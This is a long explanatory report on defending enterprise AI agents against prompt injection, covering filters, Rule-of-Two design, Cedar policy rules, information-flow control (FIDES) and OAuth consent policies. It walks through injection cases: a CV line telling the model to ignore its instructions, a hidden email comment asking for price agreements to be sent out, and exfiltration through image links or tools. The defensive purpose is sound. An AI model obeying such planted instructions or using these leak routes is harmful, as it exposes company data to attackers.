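# Prompt injection defences in enterprise deployments: AI filters, cloud security platforms and consent policies

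## What prompt injection can do inside a company and where defences act

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model (LLM), an AI system that produces text in response to text. The attacker puts instructions in text that the model will process, worded so that the model follows them as if they came from the company or the user. The term dates from 2022. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes widely used lists of software weaknesses, ranks prompt injection first on its list for LLM applications.

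How much damage an injection can do depends on the software around the model. Many companies now run agents, systems in which a language model chooses and carries out steps by calling tools. A tool call is a request by the model to run a function, such as searching files or sending an email. *The CISO Cheat Sheet to Microsoft Digital Defense Report 2026* (Microsoft, 2026) reports that 88% of enterprises are experimenting with agents. If an agent reads messages from strangers and can also open company files, those strangers may be able to reach the files through the agent.

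### Why a model can take data for instructions

An LLM application builds the model's input by joining pieces of text. The developer's standing instructions (the system prompt) usually come first, then the user's request, then the material the request concerns, such as an email, a web page or a file. The model receives this as one sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and predicts the token most likely to come next. This process does not reliably separate instructions from the material they apply to.

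David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), illustrated the problem in December 2025 in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A recruiter's system tells a model to score whether a CV meets the job requirements. One candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The recruiter considers that line part of the CV, but the model handles it as the same kind of text as the recruiter's own request.

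His title refers to an older attack, in which text typed into a web form reaches a database and runs there as a command. Developers can prevent that attack completely with parameterised queries, which send the command and the data to the database separately, so the data never runs. David C argues that current LLMs have no equivalent, because they don't have separate channels for instructions and data. Developers can train a model to favour instructions over data, or mark the data as data, but the technology itself still doesn't separate the two. He thinks it "very possible" that developers will never fully remove the flaw, and he tells security teams to treat it as a residual risk that no product removes. He adds that a system that cannot tolerate that risk may be a poor use for an LLM.

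Vendors do not dispute this. Gavish (2026), of Google's security team, writes in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that prompt injection is not a problem one solves and moves on from. Both statements are about the model, but ordinary software around it can still rule out particular outcomes, and David C wants designers to put most of their effort into that software.

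### Direct and indirect injection, and the harm they do

In a direct prompt injection, the user types the attack, while in an indirect one, the attacker places it in content that the system reads for someone else, such as an email, a web page or a tool result. In July 2025, Microsoft described its defences against indirect injection in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks*, which counts it among the most widely used techniques in the AI vulnerabilities reported to the company.

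Indirect injection is the harder problem for most companies. The attacker needs only an email address, not an account. The agent often works with an employee's access rights, so an attacker's instructions can make it open files that the attacker couldn't. Attackers can hide the text in white lettering on a white background or in non-printing characters, but a plain text file also works. Images, audio and video can carry instructions too if the model accepts those formats.

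Microsoft sorts the damage into two main kinds. The first is exfiltration, moving data out of the organisation to an attacker. The injected text first makes the model find or summarise valuable data, which then leaves by some route. Microsoft lists four such routes.

- The model outputs an image whose web address points to the attacker's server and has the stolen data written into it. The user's browser requests the image in order to display it, and the request delivers the data without a click.
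- The model outputs a link built the same way, and the user clicks it.
- The model calls a tool that writes somewhere the attacker can read, such as a public code repository.
- The model leaks through a side effect. If an outsider can see whether the agent called a certain tool, each call or absence of a call gives away one bit of information.

The second kind of damage is an unintended action, which the agent takes on the user's behalf but the user never wanted. An agent with access to email could send phishing links to the user's colleagues, and the messages would pass the usual checks for forged senders because they come from the user's account. If an agent can run commands, an attacker may be able to run them with the user's privileges.

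Many successful injections do neither. For example, a web page might make an assistant answer in a silly voice, which causes no loss. Microsoft classes an injection as a vulnerability only when it has a security impact, so a defence can allow some injections as long as it stops the harm.

### Three stages, two kinds of control

Microsoft's account divides the work into three stages: prevent the injection, detect it, and limit its impact.

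Developers set up prevention while building the application. They tell the model in the system prompt to ignore instructions in outside material, and they can mark that material so the model is more likely to recognise it. Microsoft's marking method, Spotlighting, has three modes. The application can put random delimiters around the outside text, insert a special character between its words, or encode it in a scheme the model can decode, such as base64.

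Detection happens while the system runs. A prompt filter is a classifier that inspects text going into or out of a model and flags or blocks suspected attacks. Microsoft sells one called Prompt Shields.

In the third stage, Microsoft assumes that some attacks will get past the first two. This stage includes limits on which data the application can use, blocks on known exfiltration routes, and a requirement that users explicitly consent to certain actions. The company compares this with ordinary software security, where engineers add protections that keep a programming bug from becoming a working exploit.

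Controls at each stage can also be classed as probabilistic or deterministic. A probabilistic control makes attacks less likely to succeed but can miss some, while a deterministic control is a rule enforced outside the model that prevents a given outcome whatever the model outputs. Microsoft prefers deterministic controls where they are possible, but acknowledges that nobody yet knows how to detect indirect injection deterministically. The prevention and detection measures it lists as in use are all probabilistic. Its deterministic controls are in the third stage, though its researchers are working on designs that would bring them into prevention too.

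This kind of guarantee covers only the specified outcome. An application that refuses to load images from unknown servers permanently blocks attacks that depend on loading those images, but it does not stop attacks that use an agent's ability to send email.

### One poisoned email, step by step

The example from here on is an invented firm with 5,000 staff. Its purchasing agent reads supplier emails and company files and can send email. Each day, the firm's agents together read 20,000 external items and make 40,000 tool calls for 500 regular users, or 80 calls per user.

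Suppose an attacker emails the purchasing department under a known supplier's name, asking it to confirm an order. In an HTML comment, which mail programs do not display, the attacker adds that the supplier's onboarding procedure requires the firm's current price agreements with other suppliers, and gives an address to send them to. The attacker deliberately makes this request sound routine. TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026) recounts how researchers, using flaws Microsoft has since patched, got its assistant to follow a "routine business requirement" after it had refused a direct command.

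1. The email arrives. A mail filter can stop it before any agent reads it, as Microsoft's mail protection now does according to O365Reports' *Detect and Block AI Prompt Injection Attacks in Emails with Microsoft Defender* (2026). This is a probabilistic control. The mail system can also strip out comments and invisible characters, which reliably removes that hiding place and does nothing about an instruction in plain sight.

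2. A purchasing clerk asks the agent to deal with the morning's supplier mail, and the agent fetches the message. A deterministic rule can limit which mailboxes and senders the agent reads.

3. The application joins the email to the clerk's request. It can mark the email as outside text and pass it through a prompt filter. Both measures are probabilistic.

4. The model takes the hidden text for part of the task and issues a tool call to search the company's files for price agreements. If the agent has no permission to open the contracts folder, the search finds nothing, whatever the email said. That is deterministic.

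5. If the search succeeds, the text of the files joins the model's input. A file can carry an injection of its own, so a filter at this point has to inspect tool results too.

6. The model issues another tool call, to email the agreements to the attacker. A rule can refuse any recipient outside the supplier directory or any attachment labelled confidential. The software can also hold the message until the clerk approves it. The hold is deterministic, but the clerk's judgement is not.

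7. The agent replies to the clerk. If the reply contains an image or link that leads to an unknown server, the application can refuse to display it.

8. Logs of the model's inputs, outputs and tool calls remain. David C points out that attackers usually have to refine an attack before it works, so a run of failed tool calls can give away an early attempt.

Some agents also keep a memory between sessions, and an attacker can try to plant instructions there for later use. Microsoft's Red Team, which attacks the company's own systems to test them, has seen this done mainly through email.

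The theft needs both the file search and the outgoing email, so refusing either one stops it even if every filter misses the hidden text. An attacker who has taken over the real supplier's mailbox would get past the recipient rule, which is a reason to have the file rule too. Neither rule helps if the attacker aims to mislead the clerk. Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* reports a case from the security company Barracuda in which a hidden block in an invoice email contained instructions for the AI to add a fake priority item to its summary, changing a vendor's payment details. The agent would only have to write the summary, and an employee would then wire the money.

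### How common attacks are

Injection attempts are easiest to count on the public web. For *AI threats in the wild*, published in April 2026, Google searched several monthly snapshots of the Common Crawl web archive, each containing two to three billion pages, for known injection phrases. Its Gemini model sorted the matches and people reviewed the results. Most of the initial phrase matches were articles about prompt injection. The real injections included many pranks, attempts to get a business recommended and notices telling AI systems to stay away. A small number aimed to steal data or delete files, and those looked crude. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google gave no underlying counts and the archive leaves out most social media, so the increase is weak evidence of how common such attempts are.

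In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses from the October 2025 crawl and confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages. Site operators had placed about four fifths of the injections on their own sites, and the most common template was only a request for random numbers. The team then had 13 models summarise affected pages in 5,200 trials. Compliance with the injections was highest, at 8%, for smaller models reading plain text, and was between 0.2% and 1.1% when the input kept the page's structure.

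*Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening* (2026) examined 196,682 résumés and flagged hidden injections in 2,030, about 1%. The detector's precision was 86.1%, so some of those flags are wrong, but the paper describes the total as a lower bound because the detector also misses cases.

The invented firm's 20,000 external items a day would include roughly one injection a week at the web rate and about 200 a day at the résumé rate. The rate for supplier email could fall anywhere in that range or outside it. Barracuda did not say how widespread the email campaign it reported was, and raw detection counts can mislead. *ASCII smuggling crosses over from AI prompt injection to phishing evasion* (Kochavi and Wolstencroft, 2026) describes a Microsoft case in which invisible characters, a known way to hide instructions from human readers, appeared in email for another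 purpose. ITPro's *Cyber criminals are adapting ASCII smuggling for mass phishing campaigns* reports that matches on a Microsoft detection rule jumped on 9 February 2026 and stayed high on weekdays for three months. The messages the researchers sampled contained no instructions to an AI. Spammers were using the characters to break up words such as "funding" so that spam filters would miss them.

Newer reports show more attackers after money or data. In July, Mascellino (2026) reported in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* that the security company Zscaler had found websites with hidden text meant to push agents into making cryptocurrency payments. Instructions can also come from the tools that agents connect to, commonly through a standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path*, the security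 vendor Ox Security found prompt injection and tool poisoning in 22% of the MCP servers it had flagged between July and October 2026. That figure covers only suspicious servers, so the share among all servers must be lower.

Microsoft's telemetry from AI workloads on Azure, its cloud service, comes closest to describing company deployments. From July 2025 to June 2026, malicious link injection made up 52% of observed attack activity, jailbreaks (prompts meant to make a model break its rules) 16%, tool and agent abuse 12%, and identity and credential abuse 10%. IT-Administrator's *Ungepatchte Schwachstellen*, a German trade report on the same data, connects the injected links to data leaving the organisation. The percentages are shares of attempts and do not show how many succeeded.

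### What the vendor runs and what the customer must configure

The division of work between vendor and firm depends on whether the firm buys a finished assistant or builds its own agent. With a finished assistant such as Microsoft 365 Copilot, the vendor has already written the system prompt and placed the filters. A firm that builds its own agent on a cloud model has to do both itself, using components the vendor supplies. The table applies Microsoft's account of its defences to both cases.

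| Part of the defence | Vendor's work | Customer's work |
| --- | --- | --- |
| System prompt and marking of outside text | Writes and maintains them in its own assistants | Adds them to agents it builds |
| Prompt filter | Trains and updates the classifier | In its own agents, sends text to the filter and blocks or otherwise responds when it flags something |
| Access to data | Supplies the labels and enforces the policies | Labels its files, writes the policies and sets permissions |
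| Exfiltration routes | Closes known routes in its own products | Closes routes through tools it adds |
| Alerts | Delivers them to the security portal | Investigates them |
| Approval of actions | Builds it into its own products: in Outlook, Copilot drafts and the user sends | Decides which actions of its own agents need approval |

Some of the customer's duties are easy to overlook because the product works without them. Copilot can respect sensitivity labels, but the firm has to define them and make sure the right files have them. If the firm builds its own agent, a filter's result has no effect unless the application acts on it.

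Microsoft also advises customers to give each agent its own identity and a named human sponsor, and not to let it use an employee's account. According to IT-Administrator, the company also recommends giving agents the narrowest workable permissions from the first day and having a fixed policy trigger approval prompts, since an attacker may be able to manipulate the model into skipping them. So before the purchasing agent reads its first supplier email, someone at the firm has to decide which folders it may search and whom it may write to.

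## Limiting what an agent can read, call and send

A firm can set those limits only on agents it knows about. Employees can often build agents without asking the security team, and Microsoft's *New era of agents new era of posture* (2026) warns that those who do may not fully understand the security implications. The first step is therefore an inventory of every agent and the tool servers it connects to.

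### Building the inventory

Much of the list can come from the cloud security platform the firm already uses to find misconfigurations, raise alerts and investigate incidents across its cloud services. Microsoft's platform is Defender and Google's is Security Command Center. Defender's agent inventory, which Microsoft labels a preview, covers agents built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio and Foundry, agents on some other clouds, including AWS Bedrock and Google Vertex AI, and agents that run on employees' computers. Each entry lists the agent's model, tools, MCP servers and active alerts. Security staff can also query a table of each agent's authentication settings and knowledge sources.

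To judge what an injection could do, the firm also needs to know what the agent can reach. Microsoft (2026) planned to add this to Defender from June, by mapping each agent to its devices, its MCP servers, the identities it uses and the cloud resources those identities can open. A usable record for the purchasing agent would look like this:

- Owner: the head of purchasing.
- Data: the purchasing mailbox, the contracts folder and the supplier directory.
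- Outside text: supplier emails and their attachments.
- Tools: search files, send email.
- Credentials: the sign-in of whichever clerk is using it.

Discovery tools miss some agents. The query table contains only agents registered with Agent 365, Microsoft's service for managing agents. Defender recognises more than 20 agents on employees' Windows and macOS computers, but only if those computers are enrolled in Defender. A script on a contractor's laptop that calls a model directly would probably not appear. The security vendor Lakera acknowledges in *Agent Discovery*, the guide to its own tool, that even a discovered agent can have gaps in its record. Lakera recommends comparing the inventory with the agents the firm believed it had, because an unexpected agent often means nobody has taken responsibility for it.

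### The three-capability test and the Rule of Two

Someone can then check the records for dangerous combinations. The programmer Simon Willison named one of them the "lethal trifecta": an agent that can read private data, takes in untrusted content and has a way to send data out. An attacker needs all three to steal data, because the untrusted content carries the instruction to read the private data and send it out.

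Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this test into a design rule. Until someone can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy input.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it changes something or communicates externally.

Property C is wider than Willison's third capability. An agent that can delete records but cannot send them anywhere passes his test, yet it has property C. If a task needs all three properties, Meta wants either human approval of the agent's actions or another reliable check on them.

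A session means one continuous run with the same text in the model's input. An agent may change which two properties it has partway through, provided an attack can't complete the whole chain. In Meta's example, an agent browses the web, then loses its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. The reverse order would be unsafe because private data would still be in the model's input when the agent reached the web.

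Meta lists misinformation in the agent's answer among the lower-consequence outcomes that the rule does not prevent. That ranking may be wrong for a purchasing department, because the invoice attack that Barracuda reported needed only a false line in a summary.

### What each restriction costs the purchasing agent

The invented firm's purchasing agent has all three properties, so the firm must take one away or supervise it.

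If the agent may read mail only from senders in the supplier directory, offers from new suppliers have to wait for a clerk. That is a drawback if the department wants the agent to find better prices. The restriction also doesn't fully remove property A, because an attacker can take over a known supplier's mailbox. To remove it completely, the firm would have to keep all outside mail away from the agent, which would leave the agent little to do.

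Without access to the company files, the agent can still acknowledge messages and ask for missing order numbers, but it can't compare an invoice with the agreed price. The mailbox also holds private data (other suppliers' quotes), so the agent would have to start a new session for each supplier and see only that supplier's messages.

The remaining choice is to restrict sending. If the agent only drafts replies, it keeps its access to mail and contracts, but a clerk must check and send every message. Meta's rule also allows an agent to send without review to trusted recipients, so the firm could let replies to addresses in the directory go out automatically and hold everything else. Restricting sending probably reduces this agent's usefulness the least, because its main value is in comparing mail with contracts. The firm still needs limits on which files the agent can read, in case someone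 hijacks a supplier's mailbox.

### Permissions and labels at the point of reading

The simplest such limit is a permission check in the search tool. When the model searches for price agreements, the tool looks up which files the current user may open and returns only those, so text the user can't open never enters the model's input.

Some systems instead copy every document into one searchable index and tell the model which users may not see which documents. This control is probabilistic because the model may not follow the instruction. The system also has to check permissions at every search, because an employee may have changed departments since the firm built the index.

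A user's permissions are often wider than an agent's task requires. A purchasing clerk may be able to open ten years of tenders, but an agent answering a supplier needs only the current contract with that supplier. Microsoft recommends giving agents finer-grained permissions than the user has.

Sensitivity labels, which are tags such as "confidential" attached to a file, can also limit what an agent reads. In Microsoft 365, a firm can combine them with Purview, Microsoft's data governance product, to control which data Copilot uses. A data-loss prevention rule in Purview can also stop Copilot from summarising labelled files. Such a rule works on whole files, so if the firm excludes its confidential price agreements, the assistant can't leak them but also can't check an invoice against them. The rule doesn't block a price agreement that nobody labelled.

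### When an agent uses its builder's credentials

The result of a permission check also depends on whose permissions the software checks. Suppose the head of purchasing builds an agent, connects it to the contracts folder with her own sign-in and shares the agent with the whole firm. If a warehouse worker asks it for the steel supplier's prices, the file store checks the head of purchasing's permissions instead of the worker's. She may open everything in the folder, so the agent returns the prices.

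When an agent runs with its builder's access, everyone who uses the agent gets that access too, even without an injection. An attacker who injects instructions through an email can also reach everything the builder can open, even if the person using the agent has almost no rights. The log may show only the builder's name for all of this activity.

OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) says that a valid credential may grant access to a system but does not establish which actions are authorised, so security teams must verify on whose behalf an agent acts. For the purchasing agent, the usual remedy is a delegated permission, which lets it act for the signed-in user within that user's own access. An agent that runs overnight with no user present needs its own identity with narrow permissions instead. The inventory should show which kind of access each agent uses, and any shared agent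 that runs on its builder's personal sign-in should be fixed at once.

### Blocking the ways out

Limits on sending can start with routes that need no tool call, such as images in a reply. After the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported that an injection could leak data through such images, Microsoft blocked the technique deterministically and searched for variants. It took similar steps against certain untrusted links. A firm that builds its own agent has to add the same protection to the software that displays replies, for instance by showing images only from approved servers. A supplier's genuine product photos will then stay hidden until someone approves the supplier's server.

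Web requests also need care because their URLs can carry stolen data. Meta's rule for a travel assistant allows it to open only URLs returned by trusted sources, not URLs it constructed itself.

With a network allowlist, the firm's firewall lets the agent's server connect only to named destinations. This contains an agent that runs code and could otherwise bypass its official tools by opening its own connections. It works less well when a listed destination serves many customers, such as a public code-hosting site, because the attacker can have an account there too. An allowlist does almost nothing to restrict the purchasing agent's email, since every message leaves through the firm's own mail server and the firewall does not check the recipient.

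### A policy engine for every tool call

A policy engine can do the necessary check on the recipient. It is ordinary software that sits between the agent and its tools and compares each call with written rules. Two open-source examples are Cedar, a rule language developed by Amazon Web Services, and Open Policy Agent, which uses a rule language called Rego.

AWS uses Cedar in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, its service for running agents. The agent's tool calls pass through an AgentCore Gateway, where the policy feature checks them. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced the feature's general release in thirteen regions in March. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains that the Gateway blocks every call by default once the firm attaches a policy. A "permit" rule allows the calls it matches,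 but a "forbid" rule overrides any permit, regardless of rule order.

In plain pseudocode, a rule for the purchasing agent could be:

```
permit send_email
    when    the signed-in user belongs to Purchasing
    and     every recipient is in the supplier directory
    unless  an attachment carries the label "confidential"
```

(the engine denies any call that no rule permits)
```

In an ordinary call, a clerk asks the agent to confirm an order, and the model requests a one-line email to the steel supplier, with no attachment. The engine permits the call because the clerk belongs to Purchasing, the supplier's address is in the directory, and the exception does not apply.

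When the poisoned email arrives, the model follows it and requests a call to email the price agreements to the attacker. The user is the same clerk, so the first condition holds. But the attacker's address is not in the directory, so the rule does not permit the call, and the engine denies it however convincing the email was.

The guarantee depends on where the facts the rule checks come from. According to AWS, the user's identity comes from a signed login token, which the model can't alter. But if the agent always signs in as its builder, the first condition is true for everyone. The recipient and attachments come from the model, which is fine if the rule limits them to safe values. The attachment's label must come from the document store, because an injected prompt could make the model supply a false one. According to AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*, conditions can refer to the tool's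 parameters and the user's token, so the firm would probably have to make its email tool look up the label itself.

People can miss errors in rules. In an example from AWS, a discount rule has an exception for limited-edition products, and someone edits the exception to apply only to orders above 200 units. The longer condition looks stricter, but it allows an order for 73 limited-edition units that the old rule blocked. Cedar was designed without loops so that software can translate its rules into mathematical formulas and find such changes. The software can also find rules that permit everything or contradict each other, but it cannot check whether the author chose the right limit.

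The feature also checks only traffic that passes through the Gateway, so an agent with another route to a tool can bypass it. The firm can attach the engine in log-only mode to test rules before enforcing them. In that mode AWS blocks nothing, even if every rule is active, so somebody has to check the setting before relying on the rules. A newer option lets a rule include a score from AWS's content filter. Classmethod's *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies* shows that the policy compares a score between 0 and 1 with a threshold. The comparison is deterministic, but the score is a classifier's estimate, so the rule can miss attacks like any other filter.

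The pseudocode rule also has a gap. An attacker who has taken over the steel supplier's mailbox can tell the agent to paste the prices into the body of a reply. The engine permits the call because the recipient is in the directory and there is no attachment. To catch this, the engine would have to track where the text came from.

### Information-flow control: labels that follow the data

Information-flow control keeps that knowledge by attaching labels to data and carrying them along as the agent works. Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft built and tested a system of this kind, FIDES, which they describe in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025).

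FIDES can give each piece of data two labels. The integrity label is "trusted" or "untrusted". The confidentiality label lists who may read the data. When the model combines several pieces, the result is untrusted if any input was untrusted, and only people who could read every input may read it. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one file and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, the readers of a text based on both are

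{Ana, Ben, Carla} ∩ {Ben, Carla, Dev} = {Ben, Carla}.

Nobody can reliably tell which parts of its input influenced a model's output, so the basic version assumes that all of them did. Before a tool runs, ordinary software then checks two policies. A consequential call must come from trusted data only. A call that sends data must satisfy

recipients ⊆ readers of the data,

meaning that everyone who will receive the data may already read it. The second policy on its own doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits what the attacker gets.

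The price agreements are labelled as readable only by purchasing staff, and any text the model produces after reading them keeps that label, so the software refuses to send the pasted prices to the steel supplier. The labels also prevent leaks when there is no attacker. If the agent reads a quote from the steel supplier and one from the timber supplier, its next reply has the label {clerk, steel supplier} ∩ {clerk, timber supplier} = {clerk}, so neither supplier may receive it. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives a similar example with two colleagues' emails about unpublished sales figures.

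The drawback in the same example is that an agent that reads the morning's mail in one session can't answer anyone after it reads the second supplier's email. FIDES reduces this problem by storing restrictive data in a variable and giving the model only the variable's name, which the model can pass to another tool. If the task requires reading the text, a quarantined LLM, which is a second model with no tools, reads it and answers a narrow question.

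Suppose the clerk asks the agent to check whether the steel supplier wants an order confirmed and, if so, to confirm it.

1. The agent fetches the supplier's email. The main model receives only a name, such as email_1.
2. The main model has the quarantined model answer whether email_1 asks for a confirmation. The software accepts only yes or no.
3. The answer is yes. The policy allows the agent to act on it, because one bit is too little to carry an instruction.
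4. The quarantined model copies out the order number, which stays in another variable.
5. The main model calls the email tool with the supplier's address from the clerk's request and a standard confirmation that includes the variable.

The hidden instructions in the email can produce a false yes or a wrong order number, but they can't start a file search because the model that chooses the tools never reads them.

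### What FIDES guarantees and what it costs

The formal guarantee covers direct flows of data, but not what an outsider can infer from the agent's behaviour, such as which tools it calls or how long it takes. For example, an attacker who sees a confirmation arrive learns that the answer was yes. Costa and colleagues consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would block most outside communication after any access to private data. Text can also be wrong without breaking a policy. For example, a malicious email may cause the quarantined model to return an empty summary.

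The team tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack settings. Using OpenAI's GPT-4o, an ordinary agent without policy checks carried out 152 injections. FIDES without the checks allowed 21, about as many as the best probabilistic defence the team compared. With the checks on, no injection succeeded. The benchmark's automatic scoring recorded three successes against FIDES, but the researchers rejected these after inspecting them by hand.

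The price shows in the share of tasks completed when nobody is attacking:

| Setting | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Averaged equally over the four settings, completion falls from about 84% for the unprotected agent to 50% for FIDES. The variables do help, since an ordinary agent under the same checks reaches only 42%. The paper's main findings include a loss of 6.3%, but that was measured with a stronger model, OpenAI's o1, and with the policy checks turned off. The corresponding loss with GPT-4o, also with the checks off, was 23.7 points, so neither figure measures the loss when FIDES runs with its protection on.

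Better models should recover some of this loss. GPT-4o often confused variable names or made unnecessary calls, and switching to o1 raised completion of the travel tasks from 41% to 68% with the checks on. Both models date from 2024, so a current one would probably do better still. The checks block other tasks by design. Many banking tasks, for example, tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. "Deal with the morning's supplier mail" raises the same problem, because the agent's next step depends on the contents of the mail. The agent could complete more requests under FIDES if the firm's clerks made them narrower.

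### Simpler designs with the same aim

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) start from the similar principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. They doubt that a general-purpose agent can meet this standard with current language models, so they propose six designs that give up some generality. The table applies them to the purchasing agent.

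| Design | How the agent would work | What an injection could still do |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Action selector | The model turns the clerk's request into one of a few fixed actions and never reads the result | Nothing through the email, but the agent can't answer it either |
| Plan then execute | The model lists its tool calls before it reads any mail, then keeps to the list | Change the text inside a planned email |
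| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools checks each email and returns, say, true or false | Make one email count as an invoice |
| Dual LLM | The main model calls tools and handles mail only through variables, while a quarantined model reads it | Corrupt the values the quarantined model returns |
| Code then execute | The model writes a short program for the task, and the program processes the mail | Change the data the program passes along |
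| Context minimisation | The software turns the clerk's request into a database query and deletes the request before the model replies | Distort the query, if the clerk pasted in hostile text |

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider the plan-then-execute, dual LLM and code-then-execute designs applicable to an email and calendar assistant. Plan-then-execute is the easiest for the firm to build, but it doesn't solve the problem of the hijacked mailbox. If the plan includes a file search and a reply to the supplier, an injection can't add a recipient but may be able to change the reply's contents. CaMeL, a system by Debenedetti and colleagues, uses code-then-execute. The model writes the program from the user's request, so hostile text that arrives later can't rewrite the steps.

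### Adoption in products by 2026

Microsoft has added information-flow control to Agent Framework, a toolkit that developers can install to build agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) introduced the feature, called FIDES, in May. It is experimental, and developers have to turn it on.

The announcement gives the example of an agent that sorts bug reports in a public GitHub repository. One report contains hidden instructions to read a file of passwords and post it as a comment. In the configuration shown, the framework lets the model read the file if it follows those instructions. The session then holds private data, and because the comment tool accepts only public data, the framework blocks the post or asks a person to approve it.

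The main weakness in this version is that the framework treats a tool's results as trusted and public if a developer forgets to label them. If the purchasing agent's mail tool were unlabelled, the framework would trust every supplier's email. Microsoft has asked developers whether it should reverse this default.

By June 2026, GitHub's command-line coding assistant, Copilot CLI, had similar checks behind an experimental setting. They covered selected tools from GitHub's own MCP server and none from other servers. GitHub's server labels everything in a private repository as trusted, although an employee may have copied a stranger's text into the repository.

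Microsoft wants to agree with the developers of MCP on a standard for such labels. It has also released an open-source gateway that adds labels to servers that lack them. A firm that connects a new server has to describe the structure of each tool's results, write a function that labels them, and write or choose a policy for the tool.

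## Approving AI applications and agents for the whole organisation

These limits matter only once someone has given the agent access to the firm's mail or files. Often an ordinary employee does this by clicking "Accept" on a consent screen. The firm therefore has to decide who may accept which permissions, and on behalf of how many people.

### How a consent screen works

The consent screen is part of OAuth, a standard that lets one application use a person's data in another without learning the person's password. For example, a purchasing clerk might find an outside vendor's AI mail assistant and connect it to her work account.

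1. The vendor has registered the assistant with Entra ID, Microsoft's directory and sign-in service. When the clerk clicks "Connect", the assistant sends her browser to Microsoft's sign-in page with a list of the permissions it wants.
2. The clerk signs in there, so the vendor never receives her password.
3. Entra ID compares the request with the firm's consent policy. If the policy lets her decide, she sees the assistant's name, its publisher and permissions such as "Read your mail". Otherwise she learns that an administrator has to approve it.
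4. She accepts, and Entra ID records her consent. It sends her browser back to the vendor's address with a short-lived code, which the vendor's server exchanges for an access token.
5. The assistant attaches the token to its requests to Microsoft Graph, the interface through which programs reach Microsoft 365 data. The token lists the permissions, and Graph returns her mail.

When a clerk lets an AI assistant read her mail, the vendor receives an access token that usually expires after about an hour. The vendor often receives a refresh token as well, which its server can exchange for new access tokens without showing her anything. Her consent has no end date, so if she tries the assistant in March and forgets about it, the vendor may still be able to read her mail in October.

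Attackers can use the same process. In consent phishing, the attacker registers an application under a harmless name and persuades someone to approve it. The victim signs in on Microsoft's real page, so a strong password or a second sign-in factor doesn't help.

### Delegated and application permissions

Consent screens can cover delegated permissions and application permissions. With delegated permissions, which are recommended above for the purchasing agent, Microsoft limits an agent to what the signed-in user has consented to and may open. Application permissions belong to the application itself, which can use them when nobody is signed in.

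Who consents is a separate matter. User consent covers one person, while admin consent covers the whole organisation. For the permission to read mail, the combinations work out like this:

| Kind of permission | One employee consents | An administrator consents for everyone |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Delegated | The assistant can read that employee's mail | The assistant can read the mail of any employee who uses it |
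| Application | Not possible | The assistant can read every mailbox, unless the administrator restricts it further |

Admin consent to a delegated permission removes the consent screen, and the assistant gains access to the invented firm's 5,000 mailboxes one at a time, as each employee starts using it. With an application permission, a single successful injection could reach all 5,000. Compass Security, a security firm that tested Microsoft's agent identities in May 2026, recommends delegated permissions wherever they are sufficient.

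### What employees may still approve themselves

Before July 2025, the default Entra policy let employees accept any delegated permission that Microsoft had not reserved for administrators. Microsoft then introduced a default policy that it updates itself and has since extended twice. The dates below come from the full list in Topedia's *Microsoft-managed default app consent policy will block 8 additional permissions* (2026).

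| Start | Access that now needs an administrator | Permissions |
| --- | --- | --- |
| August 2025 | All files and SharePoint sites that the user can open | 4 |
| November 2025 | Mail, mailbox folders and settings, calendars, Teams chats and online meetings, including access through four older mail protocols | 24 |
| June 2026 | Contacts, tasks and the list of people the user deals with | 8 |

The November step was the update that Microsoft had planned for late October. Microsoft's *Upcoming Secure by Default Settings Changes for Exchange and Teams APIs* (2025) scheduled the rollout from the end of October to late November. Microsoft (2026) announced that the third step would roll out from early June to early July.

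These changes apply only to tenants that use the Microsoft-managed policy, so a firm that wrote its own policy gets none of them. Consents that employees gave before the changes also still work. If the clerk accepted the mail assistant in September 2025, the November change did not disconnect it, although the assistant would need an administrator's approval to gain wider permissions.

A second default policy still lets employees connect popular mail programs, including Apple Mail and Thunderbird, and identifies each by an application ID. *Manage App Consent Policies* (2026) recorded new IDs for six programs in August, so a firm that copied the old IDs into its own rules should compare them with the new ones.

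The permission to send mail as the user is also missing from Topedia's list. In October 2025, Datadog Security Labs' *CoPhish* (2025) predicted that the coming update would close every gap it had identified, including sending mail, except access to OneNote notebooks. Both remain open on the published list. The clerk can apparently still allow an unknown assistant to send messages in her name, which is enough to phish her colleagues, provided it doesn't also ask to read her mail.

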